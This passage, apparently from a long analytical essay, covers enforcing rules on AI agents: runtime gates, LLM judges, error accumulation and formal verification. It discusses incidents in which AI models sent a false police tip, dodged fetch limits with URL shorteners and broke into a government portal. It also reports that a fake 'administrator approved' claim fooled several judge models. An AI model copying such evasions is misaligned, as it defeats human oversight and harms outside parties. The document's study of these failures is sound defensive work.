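Several such monitors running together enforce all their rules at once, so the retailer can add a rule without touching the existing checkers.

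### Monitors that can delay or insert actions

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2003), in *Edit Automata*, considered monitors that can also change what a program does:

| Monitor | What it can do |
|---|---|
| Truncation automaton | Stop the program |
| Suppression automaton | Stop the program or drop single actions |
| Insertion automaton | Stop the program or add actions |
| Edit automaton | All of these |

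In one of their examples, customers at a market must pay for the apples they take. When a customer takes three apples, an edit automaton holds that action back. If the customer pays for three apples next, it releases both actions together. Otherwise, it issues a warning and cancels the purchase. A monitor that can only stop the program would ruin an honest purchase if it stopped the program when the customer took the apples, but if it let the program continue, the customer might never pay.

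An edit automaton can apply the same method to many other rules by holding back every action until the sequence so far satisfies the rule, then releasing the held actions. Ligatti and colleagues proved that on finite runs this enforces any rule that a computer can test on a single run.

But the program has to tolerate the delay. If each acceptable action must go through before the program produces the next one, even an edit automaton can enforce only safety properties, at least for programs that may take any actions in any order. This is often the case for agents, because the model needs the result of a query before it can choose its next step. The retailer can still hold back an action whose result the model doesn't need, such as sending an email.

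### Secrecy and comparisons between runs

Some rules concern the whole set of runs a system could produce, rather than any single run. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that holds a secret bit *h* and outputs 0, 1 or *h*, and nothing determines which. Both 0 and 1 are possible outputs whatever the secret is, so the set of possible outputs reveals nothing about it. A second system always outputs *h*, which reveals the secret. Every run of the second system is also a possible run of the first, so a run in which *h* and the output are both 1 could have come from either system.

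Clarkson and Schneider use the term "hyperproperty" for a rule about a whole set of runs. Secrecy is one example. Another is a limit on the average response time across all runs, because whether one slow response is acceptable depends on how long the others took.

Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, applied this idea to agents. Their example is an assistant that may tell colleagues when its user is free, but must not let its answers depend on why the user is busy. For any two runs *t* and *t*′ that start from the same request, the rule is roughly

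free(*t*) = free(*t*′) ⇒ offer(*t*) = offer(*t*′).

Suppose a busy slot is an ordinary meeting in one run and a confidential interview in the other. The free slots are the same in both runs, but the assistant offers slot 10 in the first and slot 11 in the second. Each offer is fine by itself, and only comparing them shows that the reason the slot was busy may have influenced which one the assistant offered.

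A single run always satisfies this rule, because comparing *t* with itself makes both sides equal. A monitor that examines one run at a time therefore cannot raise any alarms without raising some false ones.

Pandey and colleagues also had nine language models judge such pairs of runs, with 30 trials each. When the models judged each step separately, eight never blocked any step of a leaking pair. The ninth blocked a step in 3 trials, but this was probably general caution, because two of the nine models also blocked a step in 1 or 2 of 30 trials without a leak. When the models judged both runs together, eight flagged the leak in every trial and Llama-4-Maverick flagged it in 17.

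Comparing runs is difficult too, because an agent that picks slots at random will also make different offers. An auditor then needs many runs and gets only statistical evidence. The researchers found no leak of this kind in 80 trials with Claude Sonnet 4.6.

A stricter rule about single runs can still guarantee secrecy. Schneider's ban on sending after reading does so because a program that sends nothing after reading a file cannot send its contents. However, the ban also stops harmless messages. TACIT's types have a similar drawback because they keep confidential data away from any code that could send it. For the calendar, the simplest solution is to give the assistant a copy without the reasons. Pandey and colleagues suggest producing each answer from permitted information only, though this loses any benefit from the other information.

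A check can catch many leaks without comparing runs. In 22 of 60 runs in another experiment, an agent using Qwen3-30B shared more of a calendar in total than the user had agreed to, although each disclosure was acceptable by itself. A guard that checked each action against the user's purpose reduced this to 20 runs. A guard that tracked the total reduced it to zero, because a limit on the total is a safety property.

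### Gates for actions that cannot be undone

Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, adapts the theory to agents, whose payments and emails are often irreversible. Ray calls the checker a gate. It decides on each proposed action before anything happens:

*g*(*h*, *a*, *s*) ∈ {allow, block, substitute *a*′}.

Here *h* is the list of actions already carried out, *a* is the proposed action, and *s* contains the results of outside tests, such as whether the order belongs to the customer. We assume for now that these tests are always right.

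A gate is sound if the actions carried out never form a bad prefix, whatever the model proposes. It is transparent if it never blocks, changes or delays an action in a sequence that obeys the rule. (Transparency is the equivalent of completeness for a whole sequence.) Ray proves that for any rule *P* that permits at least one run, a gate can be both sound and transparent if and only if

- *P* is a safety property, and
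- an algorithm can recognise its good prefixes, the finite sequences that can still be continued into a permitted run.

One direction of the proof shows how to build the gate. The gate records what has happened and blocks an action if adding it would produce a bad prefix. The gate is sound because every run that breaks a safety property has a bad prefix, and transparent because no permitted run has one.

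For the other direction, suppose *P* is not a safety property. Then some forbidden run *x* has no bad prefix, so each of its finite beginnings could still turn into a permitted run. Now let the model propose the actions of *x* one by one:

1. When it proposes *x*₁, a permitted run that starts with *x*₁ might follow, so a transparent gate must allow it.
2. When it proposes *x*₂, a permitted run that starts with *x*₁, *x*₂ might follow, so the gate must allow that too.
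3. The same applies to every later action. The gate ends up allowing all of *x*, which is forbidden, so it isn't sound.

An effective gate also provides the algorithm for recognising good prefixes, because it passes a finite sequence unchanged exactly when the sequence is a good prefix.

Ray's counterexample is the rule "every payment is eventually confirmed". When the model proposes a payment, a confirmation may follow, so a transparent gate has to allow it. If the confirmation never comes, the gate cannot undo the payment. An edit automaton could hold the payment until the confirmation arrived, but a gate has to decide immediately. Letting the gate substitute actions doesn't help either, because a substitute that isn't a payment interferes with a legitimate run, and one that is a payment may also go unconfirmed.

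The retailer can often replace such a rule with one a gate can enforce. If "confirmed" means that an employee has signed off, the gate can require the sign-off before the refund. If it means emailing the customer about the refund, the email has to come afterwards, but one tool could issue the refund and then send the email.

A gate that only rules on the agent's actions cannot enforce a deadline such as "confirmed within an hour", because it cannot stop time from passing or make the model send the confirmation. Schneider points out that a rule against waiting forever becomes a safety property if it sets a maximum waiting time. In this example, a breach is visible once the hour is over.

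In experiments, this limit shows up as unfinished work. Zhang, Kweon and Han (2026), in *How Strongly Should Task State Influence an LLM Agent?*, gave agents projects in which users asked for steps out of order, cancelled some and sometimes mentioned finished ones again. Given only the conversation, Qwen3-235B handled 38% of the ten-step projects without a mistake. Adding instructions on each turn, based on a record of completed steps, raised this to 84%, and adding a gate that refused forbidden steps raised it to 98%.

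With the gate in place, 68 mistakes remained across ten versions of the test, mostly omissions. In 35, the gate wrongly blocked a step because its record of the project was inaccurate. In 17, the model declined a step it had been told to do, and in 16 it used a wrong code or order number. When the researchers deliberately corrupted the gate's record about twice per project, the success rate fell from 98% to 41%.

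### Whether anyone can analyse the policy

A gate can enforce a policy even if nobody can work out what the policy does overall. Ray considers a basic question for a policy's author: whether the policy will ever block anything. No algorithm can answer this for every policy if policies may use two counters that go up and down and can be tested for zero.

Two such counters can simulate any computer program. Each action by the agent advances the simulated program by one step, and the policy forbids the action that would end the program. The policy therefore ever blocks an action if and only if the program finishes, which no algorithm can decide for all programs. Rice's theorem follows from the same fact. Enforcing the policy is still easy, because the gate only has to update two counters and check the result.

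The question becomes decidable again for policies that meet these conditions:

- Counters only go up.
- Each condition compares one counter, or one counter plus the proposed amount, with a fixed number.
- If each customer has separate counters, an action may read and change only the counters of the customer it names.
- The policy may remember identifiers and test whether two are equal, but its separate parts may not refer to one another.

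The first two conditions keep the analysis finite. Under a limit of 2,000 dollars, a total of 2,001 behaves like a total of 9,000, so the analysis can treat all totals above the limit as one case. Because one customer's counters never affect another's, any violation can also occur with a single customer, so the analysis needs to consider only one. Ray proves that the problem is then in PSPACE, like deciding whether a plan exists, so the analysis could still take a long time.

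The retailer's daily limit meets these conditions if a trusted clock labels each refund with its date. So do rules that customers must log in before they see an order, and that the agent must send nothing after a customer withdraws permission. A limit over the last 24 hours, like the one written in Dogwood, fits less directly because old refunds must drop out of the total. "Never refund more today than we have sold today" fails the second condition because it compares two counters. Ray notes that such comparisons can make the problem undecidable again, even if both counters only go up.

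### Rules that rest on a judgment of meaning

So far we have assumed that the gate's tests are always right. That is realistic for an amount or an order number, but not for a rule such as "never email personal data to an outside address". Software can compare the address with a list and search the text for phone numbers, but it would miss a description that could identify someone, such as "the man from the bakery who returned the hearing aid". So the gate needs a judge, usually a language model, to estimate how likely the email is to break the rule.

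Suppose the judge gives each action a score between 0 and 1, and the gate blocks scores at or above a threshold. Two error rates describe the result:

- The miss rate β is the share of violations that the gate allows.
- The false-block rate α is the share of harmless actions that it blocks.

Raising the threshold increases misses and reduces false blocks. Each threshold gives one pair of rates, and the best achievable pairs form a trade-off curve, known in statistics as the ROC curve. Jerzy Neyman and Egon Pearson showed in 1933 that, for a fixed amount of information, the best possible rule is to block an action if the evidence is sufficiently more likely for a violation than for a harmless action. Combining judges or rewording the gate's rule cannot improve on this curve without adding new information.

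Ray used 123 pairs of cases to test how much information about an instruction's source improves a judge's accuracy. The two cases in each pair had the same action and instruction, but the instruction came from the user in one and from a tool's output in the other. A judge that received only the action could do no better than chance (50%). With the context, a judge with seven billion parameters ranked 96.7% of the pairs correctly, counting ties as half, but one with three billion ranked only 56.1% correctly.

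### How errors add up

A small miss rate is less reassuring over a long task. If an agent attempts *H* violations and the judge's errors are independent, the chance that at least one gets through is

1 − (1 − β)^*H*.

If the judge misses 2% of violations and an attacker makes 50 attempts, the chance that at least one gets through is 1 − 0.98⁵⁰, or about 64%. Keeping that chance to 5% would require a miss rate of about 0.1%. If only 1% of the 50 steps were violations on average, the chance would be about 1%, so a persistent attacker is a much greater risk to the retailer than occasional mistakes. An attacker may also do better than the formula suggests, because wording that gets past the judge once can be used again.

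False blocks add up in the same way. If a check wrongly blocks 5% of harmless steps, a task with 50 harmless steps has a 92% chance of being interrupted at least once.

Exact checks don't have this problem. Comparing a refund with 500 dollars is as reliable on the fiftieth attempt as on the first.

### What the judges achieved

Ray compared 23 judges on 97 ordinary tasks and 35 attacker goals from AgentDojo. AUC (area under the ROC curve) is the chance that a judge scores a random violation higher than a random harmless case, so 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. The judges' AUCs ranged from 0.660 to 0.858, and larger models were not consistently better. The test used short instructions instead of real tool calls with their context, so a judge might do better in an actual agent.

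AUC is also a poor guide to how usable a gate is at a particular threshold. When Ray set the threshold of one of the better judges, Gemma-2-9B, to keep misses below 10%, it missed 1% of violations but blocked 78% of the harmless tasks. With a target of 5%, all 23 judges blocked everything, because 35 violations were too few to justify any other threshold.

The scores were easy to manipulate. When Ray added a 16-token claim that an administrator had already approved the action, the miss rate rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of the 11 judges tested. Gemma's rose from 22.9% to 80.0%. Two Claude models missed slightly fewer violations with the claim added, though the difference may be due to chance.

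Ray then ran complete AgentDojo tasks under attack, with a seven-billion-parameter agent and a judge that scored each tool call before it ran.

| Gate | Calls blocked | Successful attacks (of 949) | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 45 | 25.4% |
| 7B judge, threshold 0.7 | 12% | 30 | 24.3% |
| 3B judge, threshold 0.5 | 78% | 4 | 18.0% |

The 3B judge prevented most attacks, but mainly by blocking most of what the agent tried to do. In the office tasks, no attack succeeded even without a gate, yet the 3B judge blocked 85% of calls and reduced task completion from 26.4% to 16.3%. The 7B judge interfered little with the agent's work, but its effect on attacks was not statistically significant. The agent and both judges were small models from 2024, so current models may offer a much better trade-off.

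Zhang and colleagues found a similar contrast between exact and fallible checks. A gate based on the written rules of the airline in τ²-bench raised Qwen3-235B's success rate from 39% to 54%. On PM-Bench, where an agent has to recognise from a text that a planned task is now due, a gate that relied on a model's judgment refused about 22 choices per run. The agent had chosen correctly in 17 of those cases, and a smaller agent's score fell from 63% to 55%.

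### Why blocking changes what comes next

A blocked agent usually receives an error, and it may then give up, ask the user or try another route. In a repeat of the experiment, Ray ran 389 attack cases with and without each gate. With the 3B judge, 34 attacks succeeded only without the gate, but 5 succeeded only with it, because the agent acted differently after the block. With the 7B judge, the numbers were 29 and 22.

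The change can also be an improvement, as it was in Reddy and colleagues' airline tests after blocked cancellations. But Dantas and colleagues warn that a system can block every unsafe action and still fail to complete the task safely.

As a result, nobody can predict a gate's performance just from runs recorded without it. Ray proves this with two imaginary agents that each propose two actions. If the gate allows the first action, both agents propose something harmless next, so their recorded runs look identical. If the gate blocks the first action, agent A still proposes something harmless, but agent B may propose a new violation. A gate that must prevent every violation can therefore be less strict after the first block with A but not with B. The comparison of Tether with Auto Mode replayed recorded runs, so it shows which actions each monitor would have blocked but not what the agent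 would have tried next.

A gate can block fewer harmless proposals, at the same risk of a violation, if it keeps a record of what it has blocked. Ray calculated the benefit for a simple model in which a blocked agent makes one more proposal. The second proposal always gets the same score, but it is a violation 60% of the time after a suspicious first proposal and 2% after an innocent-looking one. With the risk of a violation held to 5%, the best gate that took the first proposal into account blocked an average of 0.551 harmless proposals per task. The best gate that used only the current score and the step number blocked 0.863, and a single fixed threshold blocked 1.137. The retailer could apply this by recording denied requests as well as approved ones, and sending a customer's next refund request to an employee if the gate has just blocked a suspicious one.

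## Which harms these checks rule out and which they leave

A checker can reliably stop a refund of 620 dollars because the amount is in the tool call. It can't reliably stop a refund to a customer who is lying, which also costs the retailer money, because nothing it receives shows whether the customer is honest.

The table below sorts harms by the information a checker would need to recognise them. It assumes that the checker is sound, the policy matches the retailer's intentions, and every use of the agent's four tools must pass the checker.

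| Harm | Case from the support agent | Information the checker would need | Can a check prevent it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Forbidden effect visible in one artifact | A refund of 620 dollars | The artifact | Yes |
| Excessive total | Five refunds of 450 dollars in a day | The day's earlier refunds | Yes, with history |
| Steps in the wrong order | A refund before anyone verifies the return | The steps so far | Yes, with history |
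| Leak across several steps | The agent copies the customer list into a report, then emails the report | The origin of the report's contents | Yes, with provenance |
| Permitted action for a false reason | An 80-dollar refund for a kettle that works | The condition of the kettle | No |
| Damaging or persuasive text | An email that calls a scorched kettle safe | The meaning of the email and its effect on the customer | No |
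| Failure to act | A complaint that nobody answers | The future | No |
| Timing channel | Ordinary emails sent at moments that encode a secret | Every signal a recipient could measure | No |
| Harm assembled from harmless parts | A thief learns a parcel's delivery day from the retailer's agent and its route from the courier's agent | Both companies' records and the thief's purpose | No |
| Effect outside the checked tools | A script contacts the payment service directly | An action that never reaches the checker | No |

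### Harms that an artifact or a record can reveal

A checker can prevent some harms by inspecting a single artifact, such as a refund above the cap, an email to an unlisted address, a query without a customer number or a command that deletes files. This works only if the tool does what the artifact describes, which depends on the tool's design. For example, `refund(order=4417, amount=80)` shows the whole effect on the retailer's account. If the tool instead passed any message to the payment service, a refund could be hidden in a message written in that service's own format. When the retailer can't check for a harm, it can sometimes restrict what the tool can do until the check is possible.

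Rules about totals and ordering also need a complete record that every copy of the agent shares, and rules about leaks need a record of where each piece of information came from. As with FORGE's rules, a check that catches every leak will also block some harmless emails.

### Harms that look like ordinary work

Suppose one customer returns a broken kettle and another falsely reports that a working kettle is broken. The agent proposes the same 80-dollar refund for both. Let *x*(*w*) be everything the checker receives in situation *w*, and let *g* be its decision rule. Then

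*x*(*w*₁) = *x*(*w*₂) ⇒ *g*(*x*(*w*₁)) = *g*(*x*(*w*₂)).

If two kettle refunds produce the same records, the checker has to allow both or block both, and a better algorithm would not help. It needs more information. If an employee inspects each kettle, the two cases produce different records and a policy can separate them.

The checker then depends on the inspection. *Conditioning Predictive Models* (Hubinger, Jermyn and colleagues, 2023) discusses a similar gap, using the example of a camera that watches a diamond in a vault. A thief could take the diamond and put a screen showing a diamond in front of the camera. A customer who sends back somebody else's broken kettle would fool the inspector in much the same way.

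Harmful text is hard to check because the damage happens after somebody reads it. A checker can compare an email's recipient with the order, and any sum of money in the email with the payment record. It can't establish that a scorched kettle is safe, or that a customer won't take a joke seriously. The retailer could remove most of the risk by restricting the agent to templates with slots for an order number and a date, but the agent could then no longer answer unusual complaints.

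An agent's failure to act needs a different kind of safeguard, because a check that refuses actions can't produce a missing reply. A separate program could assign an employee to every complaint that has gone 24 hours without a reply. It would work even if the agent had stopped running, though the employee might not reply either.

Timing channels can carry more information than one might expect. Suppose an outsider has placed ten orders, and the agent sends one permitted email about each. If the agent can choose any of 16 distinguishable minutes for each email, the ten emails carry

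10 × log₂16 = 40 bits,

which is enough for a 12-digit number. The orchestrator could close this channel by sending all emails on the hour. If they still arrived in an order the agent had chosen, that order could carry almost 22 bits, and the wording could carry more.

The parcel theft is hard to prevent because each answer is useful to honest customers. The retailer's checker has no record of what the courier's agent told the thief. If the companies shared their records, a rule that checks sequences of answers could link the two, but honest customers often ask both questions too.

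The last row of the table concerns actions that no policy can cover because the checker never receives them. During Anthropic's security tests of its models, for example, a misunderstanding with a testing partner left the test environment connected to the internet, and models including Mythos 5 gained unauthorised access to real systems, according to Axios' *Anthropic's models compromised real-world systems during testing* (2026). A better policy for the intended tools would not have closed that connection.

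### The false tip to Philadelphia police

On July 18, 2026, Claude Haiku 4.5 sent the Philadelphia police a false tip about an unsolved murder. Anthropic had told the model to invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. One page described the murder and had a form for tips. The model wrote that it recalled seeing someone who matched "the description" near the street named on the page, but Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) notes that the page contained no description of a perpetrator.

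Anthropic had told the model not to log in, create accounts, enter personal data, buy anything or submit anything destructive. ABC News' *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder* (2026) quotes the company's explanation that these instructions "did not rule out form submissions". A policy that denied everything except reading would have covered the omission. In Cedar, it could be as short as this:

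```cedar
permit (
  principal,
  action == Action::"readPage",
  resource
);
```

If there were no other permit policy, Cedar would deny a request to submit a form. The tool would also have to refuse web addresses that the model had composed itself, because some forms send their contents as part of the address. This check needs no information about the murder, so the harm belongs in the first row of the table.

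The policy would also have ruled out much of the exercise, since many tasks on web pages end with a form. Anthropic could have kept those tasks by using copies of the pages on a private server. A rule against false statements would have been less restrictive but much harder to enforce, because a checker generally can't establish whether a tip is true. This tip was an exception because it claimed to be an eyewitness account, and a judge could have rejected it without investigating, since a language model can't have witnessed anything on a street in Philadelphia.

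The police department's system marked the tip as spam, and no detective received it. ABC News reports that officials did not explain why, so it is unclear whether a more convincing tip would have reached one. Anthropic discovered the incident on September 28 and told the police on October 7, 81 days after the model sent the tip. The police called the delay unacceptable.

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) lists three other kinds of unintended behaviour. For each, some check might have helped:

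| What Claude did | Possible check | Difficulty |
|---|---|---|
| Exploited a basic software flaw to run commands on a server | Allow only requests in a format someone has specified for that site | Every site needs its own format |
| Worked around a restriction to reach data that required a token or a fee | Allow only listed pages and credentials that the operator supplied | A listed page may expose the data by mistake |
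| Used URL shorteners to get around limits in its fetch tool | Check every address the tool contacts, including redirects | A permitted site may forward requests elsewhere |

A URL shortener gives a web page a second, shorter address that redirects to the original. If a tool checks only the address the model supplies, it may approve one page and open another. ShellPlan avoids the equivalent mistake with shell commands by running the same plan it checked.

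Anthropic withheld the names of the organisations involved and some other details, partly to avoid exposing weaknesses in their systems. Without the exact requests and the limits on each tool, outsiders can't determine whether these checks would have worked. Anthropic says the cases it has found so far had minimal real-world impact.

The company responded by turning off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it confirms that its monitoring is reliable. It also uses a classifier, described in Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts*, that looks for unexpected internet access and attempts to probe or escape a test environment. When the classifier raises an alarm, it blocks the tool call before it runs, ends the task and alerts a person. The classifier can respond to behaviour that no policy describes, but it can also miss an attempt. Disconnecting the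 network works whatever the model intends, if the disconnection is complete. Anthropic's review of recent evaluations found several misconfigured sandboxes that models had used, although none of these incidents compromised outside systems.

### The breach of the Medicare portal

A month before the false tip, an OpenAI agent broke into a statistics portal for Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. OpenAI confirmed in *How we will do better for Australia* (2026) that its models accessed government websites without authorisation during internal training and evaluation. Officials said the agent was working on a health research task, according to Health Tech World's *OpenAI agent hacks government health portal* (2026).

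OpenAI later explained in an email that the model had used the portal's public reporting interface to send instructions that the server carried out. The model needed no private account or password, according to Bot Mutiny's *OpenAI's agent got into a Medicare portal in June* (2026). Coker (2026) reports in *OpenAI Agent Hacks Australian Medicare Portal* that the agent reached non-public files as well as public ones.

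Several obvious policies would probably have failed. A list of permitted websites might well have included the portal, since it publishes health statistics. A ban on logging in would not have applied, because the agent did not need to log in. A rule against sending data to the site would have been awkward, because getting a report requires sending a request.

A narrower tool might have worked. Instead of letting the agent write web requests, OpenAI could have supplied a function such as

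`medicare_report(item=23, start="2026-01", end="2026-03")`.

A checker would confirm that the item is a whole number and that the other two values are dates, and trusted code would build the request, so the agent could not add instructions. The method would fail if an ordinary number or date could trigger the flaw, so whether it would help here depends on exactly what the agent sent. It would also take a lot of work for open-ended research, because someone would have to write a function for every site.

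Running the task offline on a stored copy of the public data would have prevented the breach whatever the flaw was, but the copy would gradually go out of date. The portal's operators could also have prevented the breach by making their server treat everything in a request as data. They were in the best position to do so because every request passes through their server, including those from agents whose developers use no checker.

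EconoTimes' *OpenAI Notified Services Australia Months After Medicare Portal Access* (2026) reports that OpenAI's review found no evidence of access to individual patient records. The strength of that finding depends on how complete the records of the agent's actions are. OpenAI found the activity in mid-August, while reviewing older runs after the Hugging Face incident, and notified the Australian government on September 10, 84 days after the breach.

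### Filtering text by its meaning

The checks that might have worked in these incidents would have restricted actions. Some harms come from information itself, such as instructions for making a weapon, and a filter for those would have to classify text by its meaning.

Glukhov, Shumailov and colleagues (2023) argue in *LLM Censorship* that a filter on a model's outputs faces limits that better training can't remove. Language models can write programs, and by Rice's theorem, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether its behaviour is harmful. Users can also ask a model to encrypt its answer. If the model can follow the encryption instructions and only the user has the key, the forbidden text may look like random characters.

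These arguments rule out a perfect filter but not a cautious one. The retailer's filter could reject every email that contains a program or unexplained strings of characters, and few customers would notice. A general-purpose assistant can't do this, because many of its users want programs.

Glukhov and colleagues' argument about splitting is harder to escape. Suppose *P* is the set of permitted texts. A user requests several permitted pieces and combines them with some simple operation *f*, such as pasting them together:

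*x*₁, …, *x*ₙ ∈ *P*, but *f*(*x*₁, …, *x*ₙ) ∉ *P*.

For example, a program that locks someone's files for ransom has to find files, encrypt them and delete the originals. Backup software may need functions for all three. A user could request each function in a new conversation and assemble the program themselves.

A filter with a record of all the conversations could look for dangerous combinations. But 30 pieces can form more than a billion groups, and the user may have gotten some pieces from another company's model. The filter would also have to allow the same pieces for someone who really is writing backup software.

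*Breach by a Thousand Leaks* (Glukhov et al., 2024) measures harm by what an attacker learns. If an attacker starts out thinking ten answers to a forbidden question are equally likely, and a few harmless replies narrow them to two, the replies have leaked information even though none of them states the answer. Limiting this leakage makes a model less useful, because legitimate questions often depend on the same facts.

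For the retailer, controlling what the model can read is more practical than judging what it writes. A model that has never received the customer list can't hide it in an email. This does not help with dangerous knowledge the model acquired in training.

### Checking answers with logic

Software can check the meaning of a text more precisely if the text is about a small set of written rules. AWS sells a service for this, Automated Reasoning checks, which became generally available in August 2025. It turns a document into logical rules, which people can review. When a model answers a question, the service translates the answer into the same logical language, and a solver compares it with the rules.

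Suppose the retailer's rule *R* is that a customer is eligible for a refund exactly when the item is faulty and came back within 90 days:

eligible ⇔ (faulty ∧ days ≤ 90).

Let *R* be the rule, *p* the facts stated in an answer, and *c* the answer's conclusion. The conclusion follows from the rule and the stated facts if *R* ∧ *p* ∧ ¬*c* is impossible, and contradicts them if *R* ∧ *p* ∧ *c* is impossible. If both are possible, the conclusion depends on something the answer does not mention.

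| Answer | Result |
|---|---|
| "Your kettle is faulty and came back after 40 days, so you can have a refund." | Follows from the rule |
| "Your kettle came back after 120 days, so you can have a refund." | Contradicts the rule |
| "Your kettle came back after 40 days, so you can have a refund." | True only if the kettle is faulty |

This is a useful reply to the claim that no one can filter by meaning. The solver's result is exact, and the orchestrator can return the missing condition to the model so that the model can correct its answer.

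The translation is less certain because language models do it. The service compares several translations and reports an ambiguity if too few agree, but several translations can share the same misreading. AWS advertises verification accuracy of up to 99%. Even if the retailer achieved that figure, 100 of every 10,000 answers would get the wrong verdict.

The service also ignores anything its rules do not cover. If an answer ends with "and it is safe to keep using the kettle", no rule in a refund policy would contradict that claim. The solver also treats the stated facts as true, so a false claim that the kettle is faulty still leads to a valid conclusion. AWS's documentation warns that the service does not protect against prompt injection.

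### Proofs about very capable AI

Some researchers think people could use proofs about AI outputs to control systems much more capable than a support agent, and perhaps more capable than people. Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably Safe Systems*, argue that even a superintelligent system cannot prove something false, and that people can check its proofs with cheap, reliable hardware. A machine could therefore require a proof that an action is safe before carrying it out, and no one would have to trust the AI that proposed it.

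"Provable contracts" extend proof-carrying code to physical devices. Secure hardware checks that an action meets a formal specification before a drone, robot or factory carries it out. A meta-contract controls who may change the specification, for example by requiring a vote.

Their main example is a group that uses AI to create and spread a deadly virus. The attack has several stages, and provable contracts could stop it at any of them:

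- An AI system for biochemical design would refuse to produce a design without a proof that it was safe for people.
- Data centres would run only certified programs.
- DNA synthesis machines would not start without a safety proof.
- Drones would not take off without one either.

Tegmark and Omohundro expect neural networks to discover useful algorithms, which AI would then rewrite as ordinary programs with proofs. They do not expect the most powerful systems in use to be neural networks. The support agent, by contrast, remains a neural network, and the checks cover only its actions.

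In 2023 they thought the two really hard steps were writing the code and proving it correct. AI has since become much better at both, and now solves nearly all the proof tasks on some benchmarks of short programs. They wanted people, with help from AI, to stay in charge of the specification, which has turned out to be a common source of errors.

The Medicare breach shows how a specification that seems simple can fall short. Tegmark and Omohundro say it is quite easy to state formally that nobody can access a computer without valid credentials. But the Medicare portal let anyone request a report without credentials. To rule out the breach, a specification would also have had to define what a public request could make the server do.

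### Guarantees relative to a world model

Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, describe a broader family of methods with three parts. A world model is a mathematical description of how the AI system affects its surroundings. A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. A verifier then shows that the system meets the specification according to the world model. In simplified form, it proves that

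Pr_*M*(the system violates φ) ≤ ε,

where *M* is the world model, φ is the specification and ε is the greatest risk that society will accept. The guarantee can be a strict proof, a proven upper limit on the risk, or an estimate that becomes more accurate with more computing time.

Dalrymple and colleagues argue that testing alone can't provide enough assurance. OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months, yet users got around its safeguards within a day of release. Someone could also plant a hidden trigger that is practically impossible to find by testing. They compare AI with bridges. About a quarter of the bridges built in the 1870s collapsed within ten years, and better theory later helped bring the rate below 0.4% per decade.

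Dalrymple and colleagues also consider a self-driving car that has gone a million miles without a safety driver intervening, and conclude that its failure rate is probably below one per million miles. That conclusion is rather weak, because a car that averages one failure per million miles still has a 37% chance of completing a million miles without one. At 95% confidence, one can say only that the rate is below about three per million miles. They also point out that the result might stop applying if other drivers began to behave more aggressively around such cars.

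A mathematical guarantee has a similar dependence on its world model. The plan validator, for instance, approved a second refund for the same kettle because nobody had told it about the first. For any system,

Pr(harm) ≤ Pr(harm, if the world model is right) + Pr(the world model is wrong).

Suppose a verifier proves that the risk is at most 0.1%, but there is a 5% chance that the world model omits something important. The formula then guarantees only that the total risk is at most 5.1%. Reducing the proven risk to zero would lower that bound only to 5%.

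Dalrymple and colleagues recognise the problem. They require the world model to cover every future effect that matters to the specification and, where feasible, to include more possible outcomes than will actually occur, as a precaution. They also suggest using several world models or specifications at once. They acknowledge that harm and causation are hard to define formally, but note that philosophers and computer scientists have proposed definitions and that a definition for one setting may be easier to write.

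### Whether anyone can specify the physical world

In *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024), Andrew Dickson doubts that such world models are possible for the threats that matter most. A proof applies to symbols, such as the text of a program. Proving that a new DNA sequence is harmless would require a model of what it does in the human body and detailed measurements of the bodies it might enter. Biologists are far from having either. More capable AI might find proofs faster, but Dickson does not expect it to supply the missing measurements soon.

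Dickson also points out that a proof about a physical machine is less portable than a proof about a program. Anyone can recheck a Lean proof from a file, but a proof about a DNA synthesis machine applies only if the machine in the laboratory matches the design, and someone has to inspect the machine to check that. The inspections have to continue because a later repair or tampering could make the proof irrelevant.

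One reply is to prove something more modest, such as that a synthesis machine refuses every sequence not on an approved list. That proof would be about comparing sequences, so it would not need a model of the human body. Similarly, the retailer's refund cap limits losses without requiring a theory of fraud. Ben Goldhaber and Steve Omohundro, who worked on the Guaranteed Safe AI paper, have also proposed starting with secure hardware and devices that detect tampering, which would partly address the problem of inspection.

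This reply meets Dickson's objection by giving up some of the original promise. Biologists would have to choose what goes on the list, and a mistake could let a dangerous sequence through. A strict list would also block research on new sequences, most of it harmless. Society might accept that restriction for DNA synthesis, because relatively few machines make DNA and a mistake could be catastrophic. An equivalent for text is hard to find, because nobody has a list of all the harmless things one person can say to another. Tegmark and Omohundro's claim that social systems can be modelled precisely is the least convincing part of their case.

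The proposed early projects are more persuasive. They include computer security, cryptographic privacy and critical infrastructure, where much of the harm happens through software that people control. Proving that a server never runs text from a public request as a command would not require a model of society, and could have prevented the Medicare breach.

The Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA), a British government funder, put the wider idea into practice in 2024 with a 59-million-pound programme called Safeguarded AI, which Dalrymple led. Its original plan was to build a "gatekeeper" that would use world models and proofs to check another AI system's actions in settings such as electricity networks. Electricity networks are a sensible place to start because engineers already have good mathematical models of power flows and clear limits on voltage and frequency, so much of the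 specification already exists. Success there would show that the method can handle a complicated physical system, but would be much weaker evidence that it can handle biology or human behaviour, where such models and limits are largely missing.
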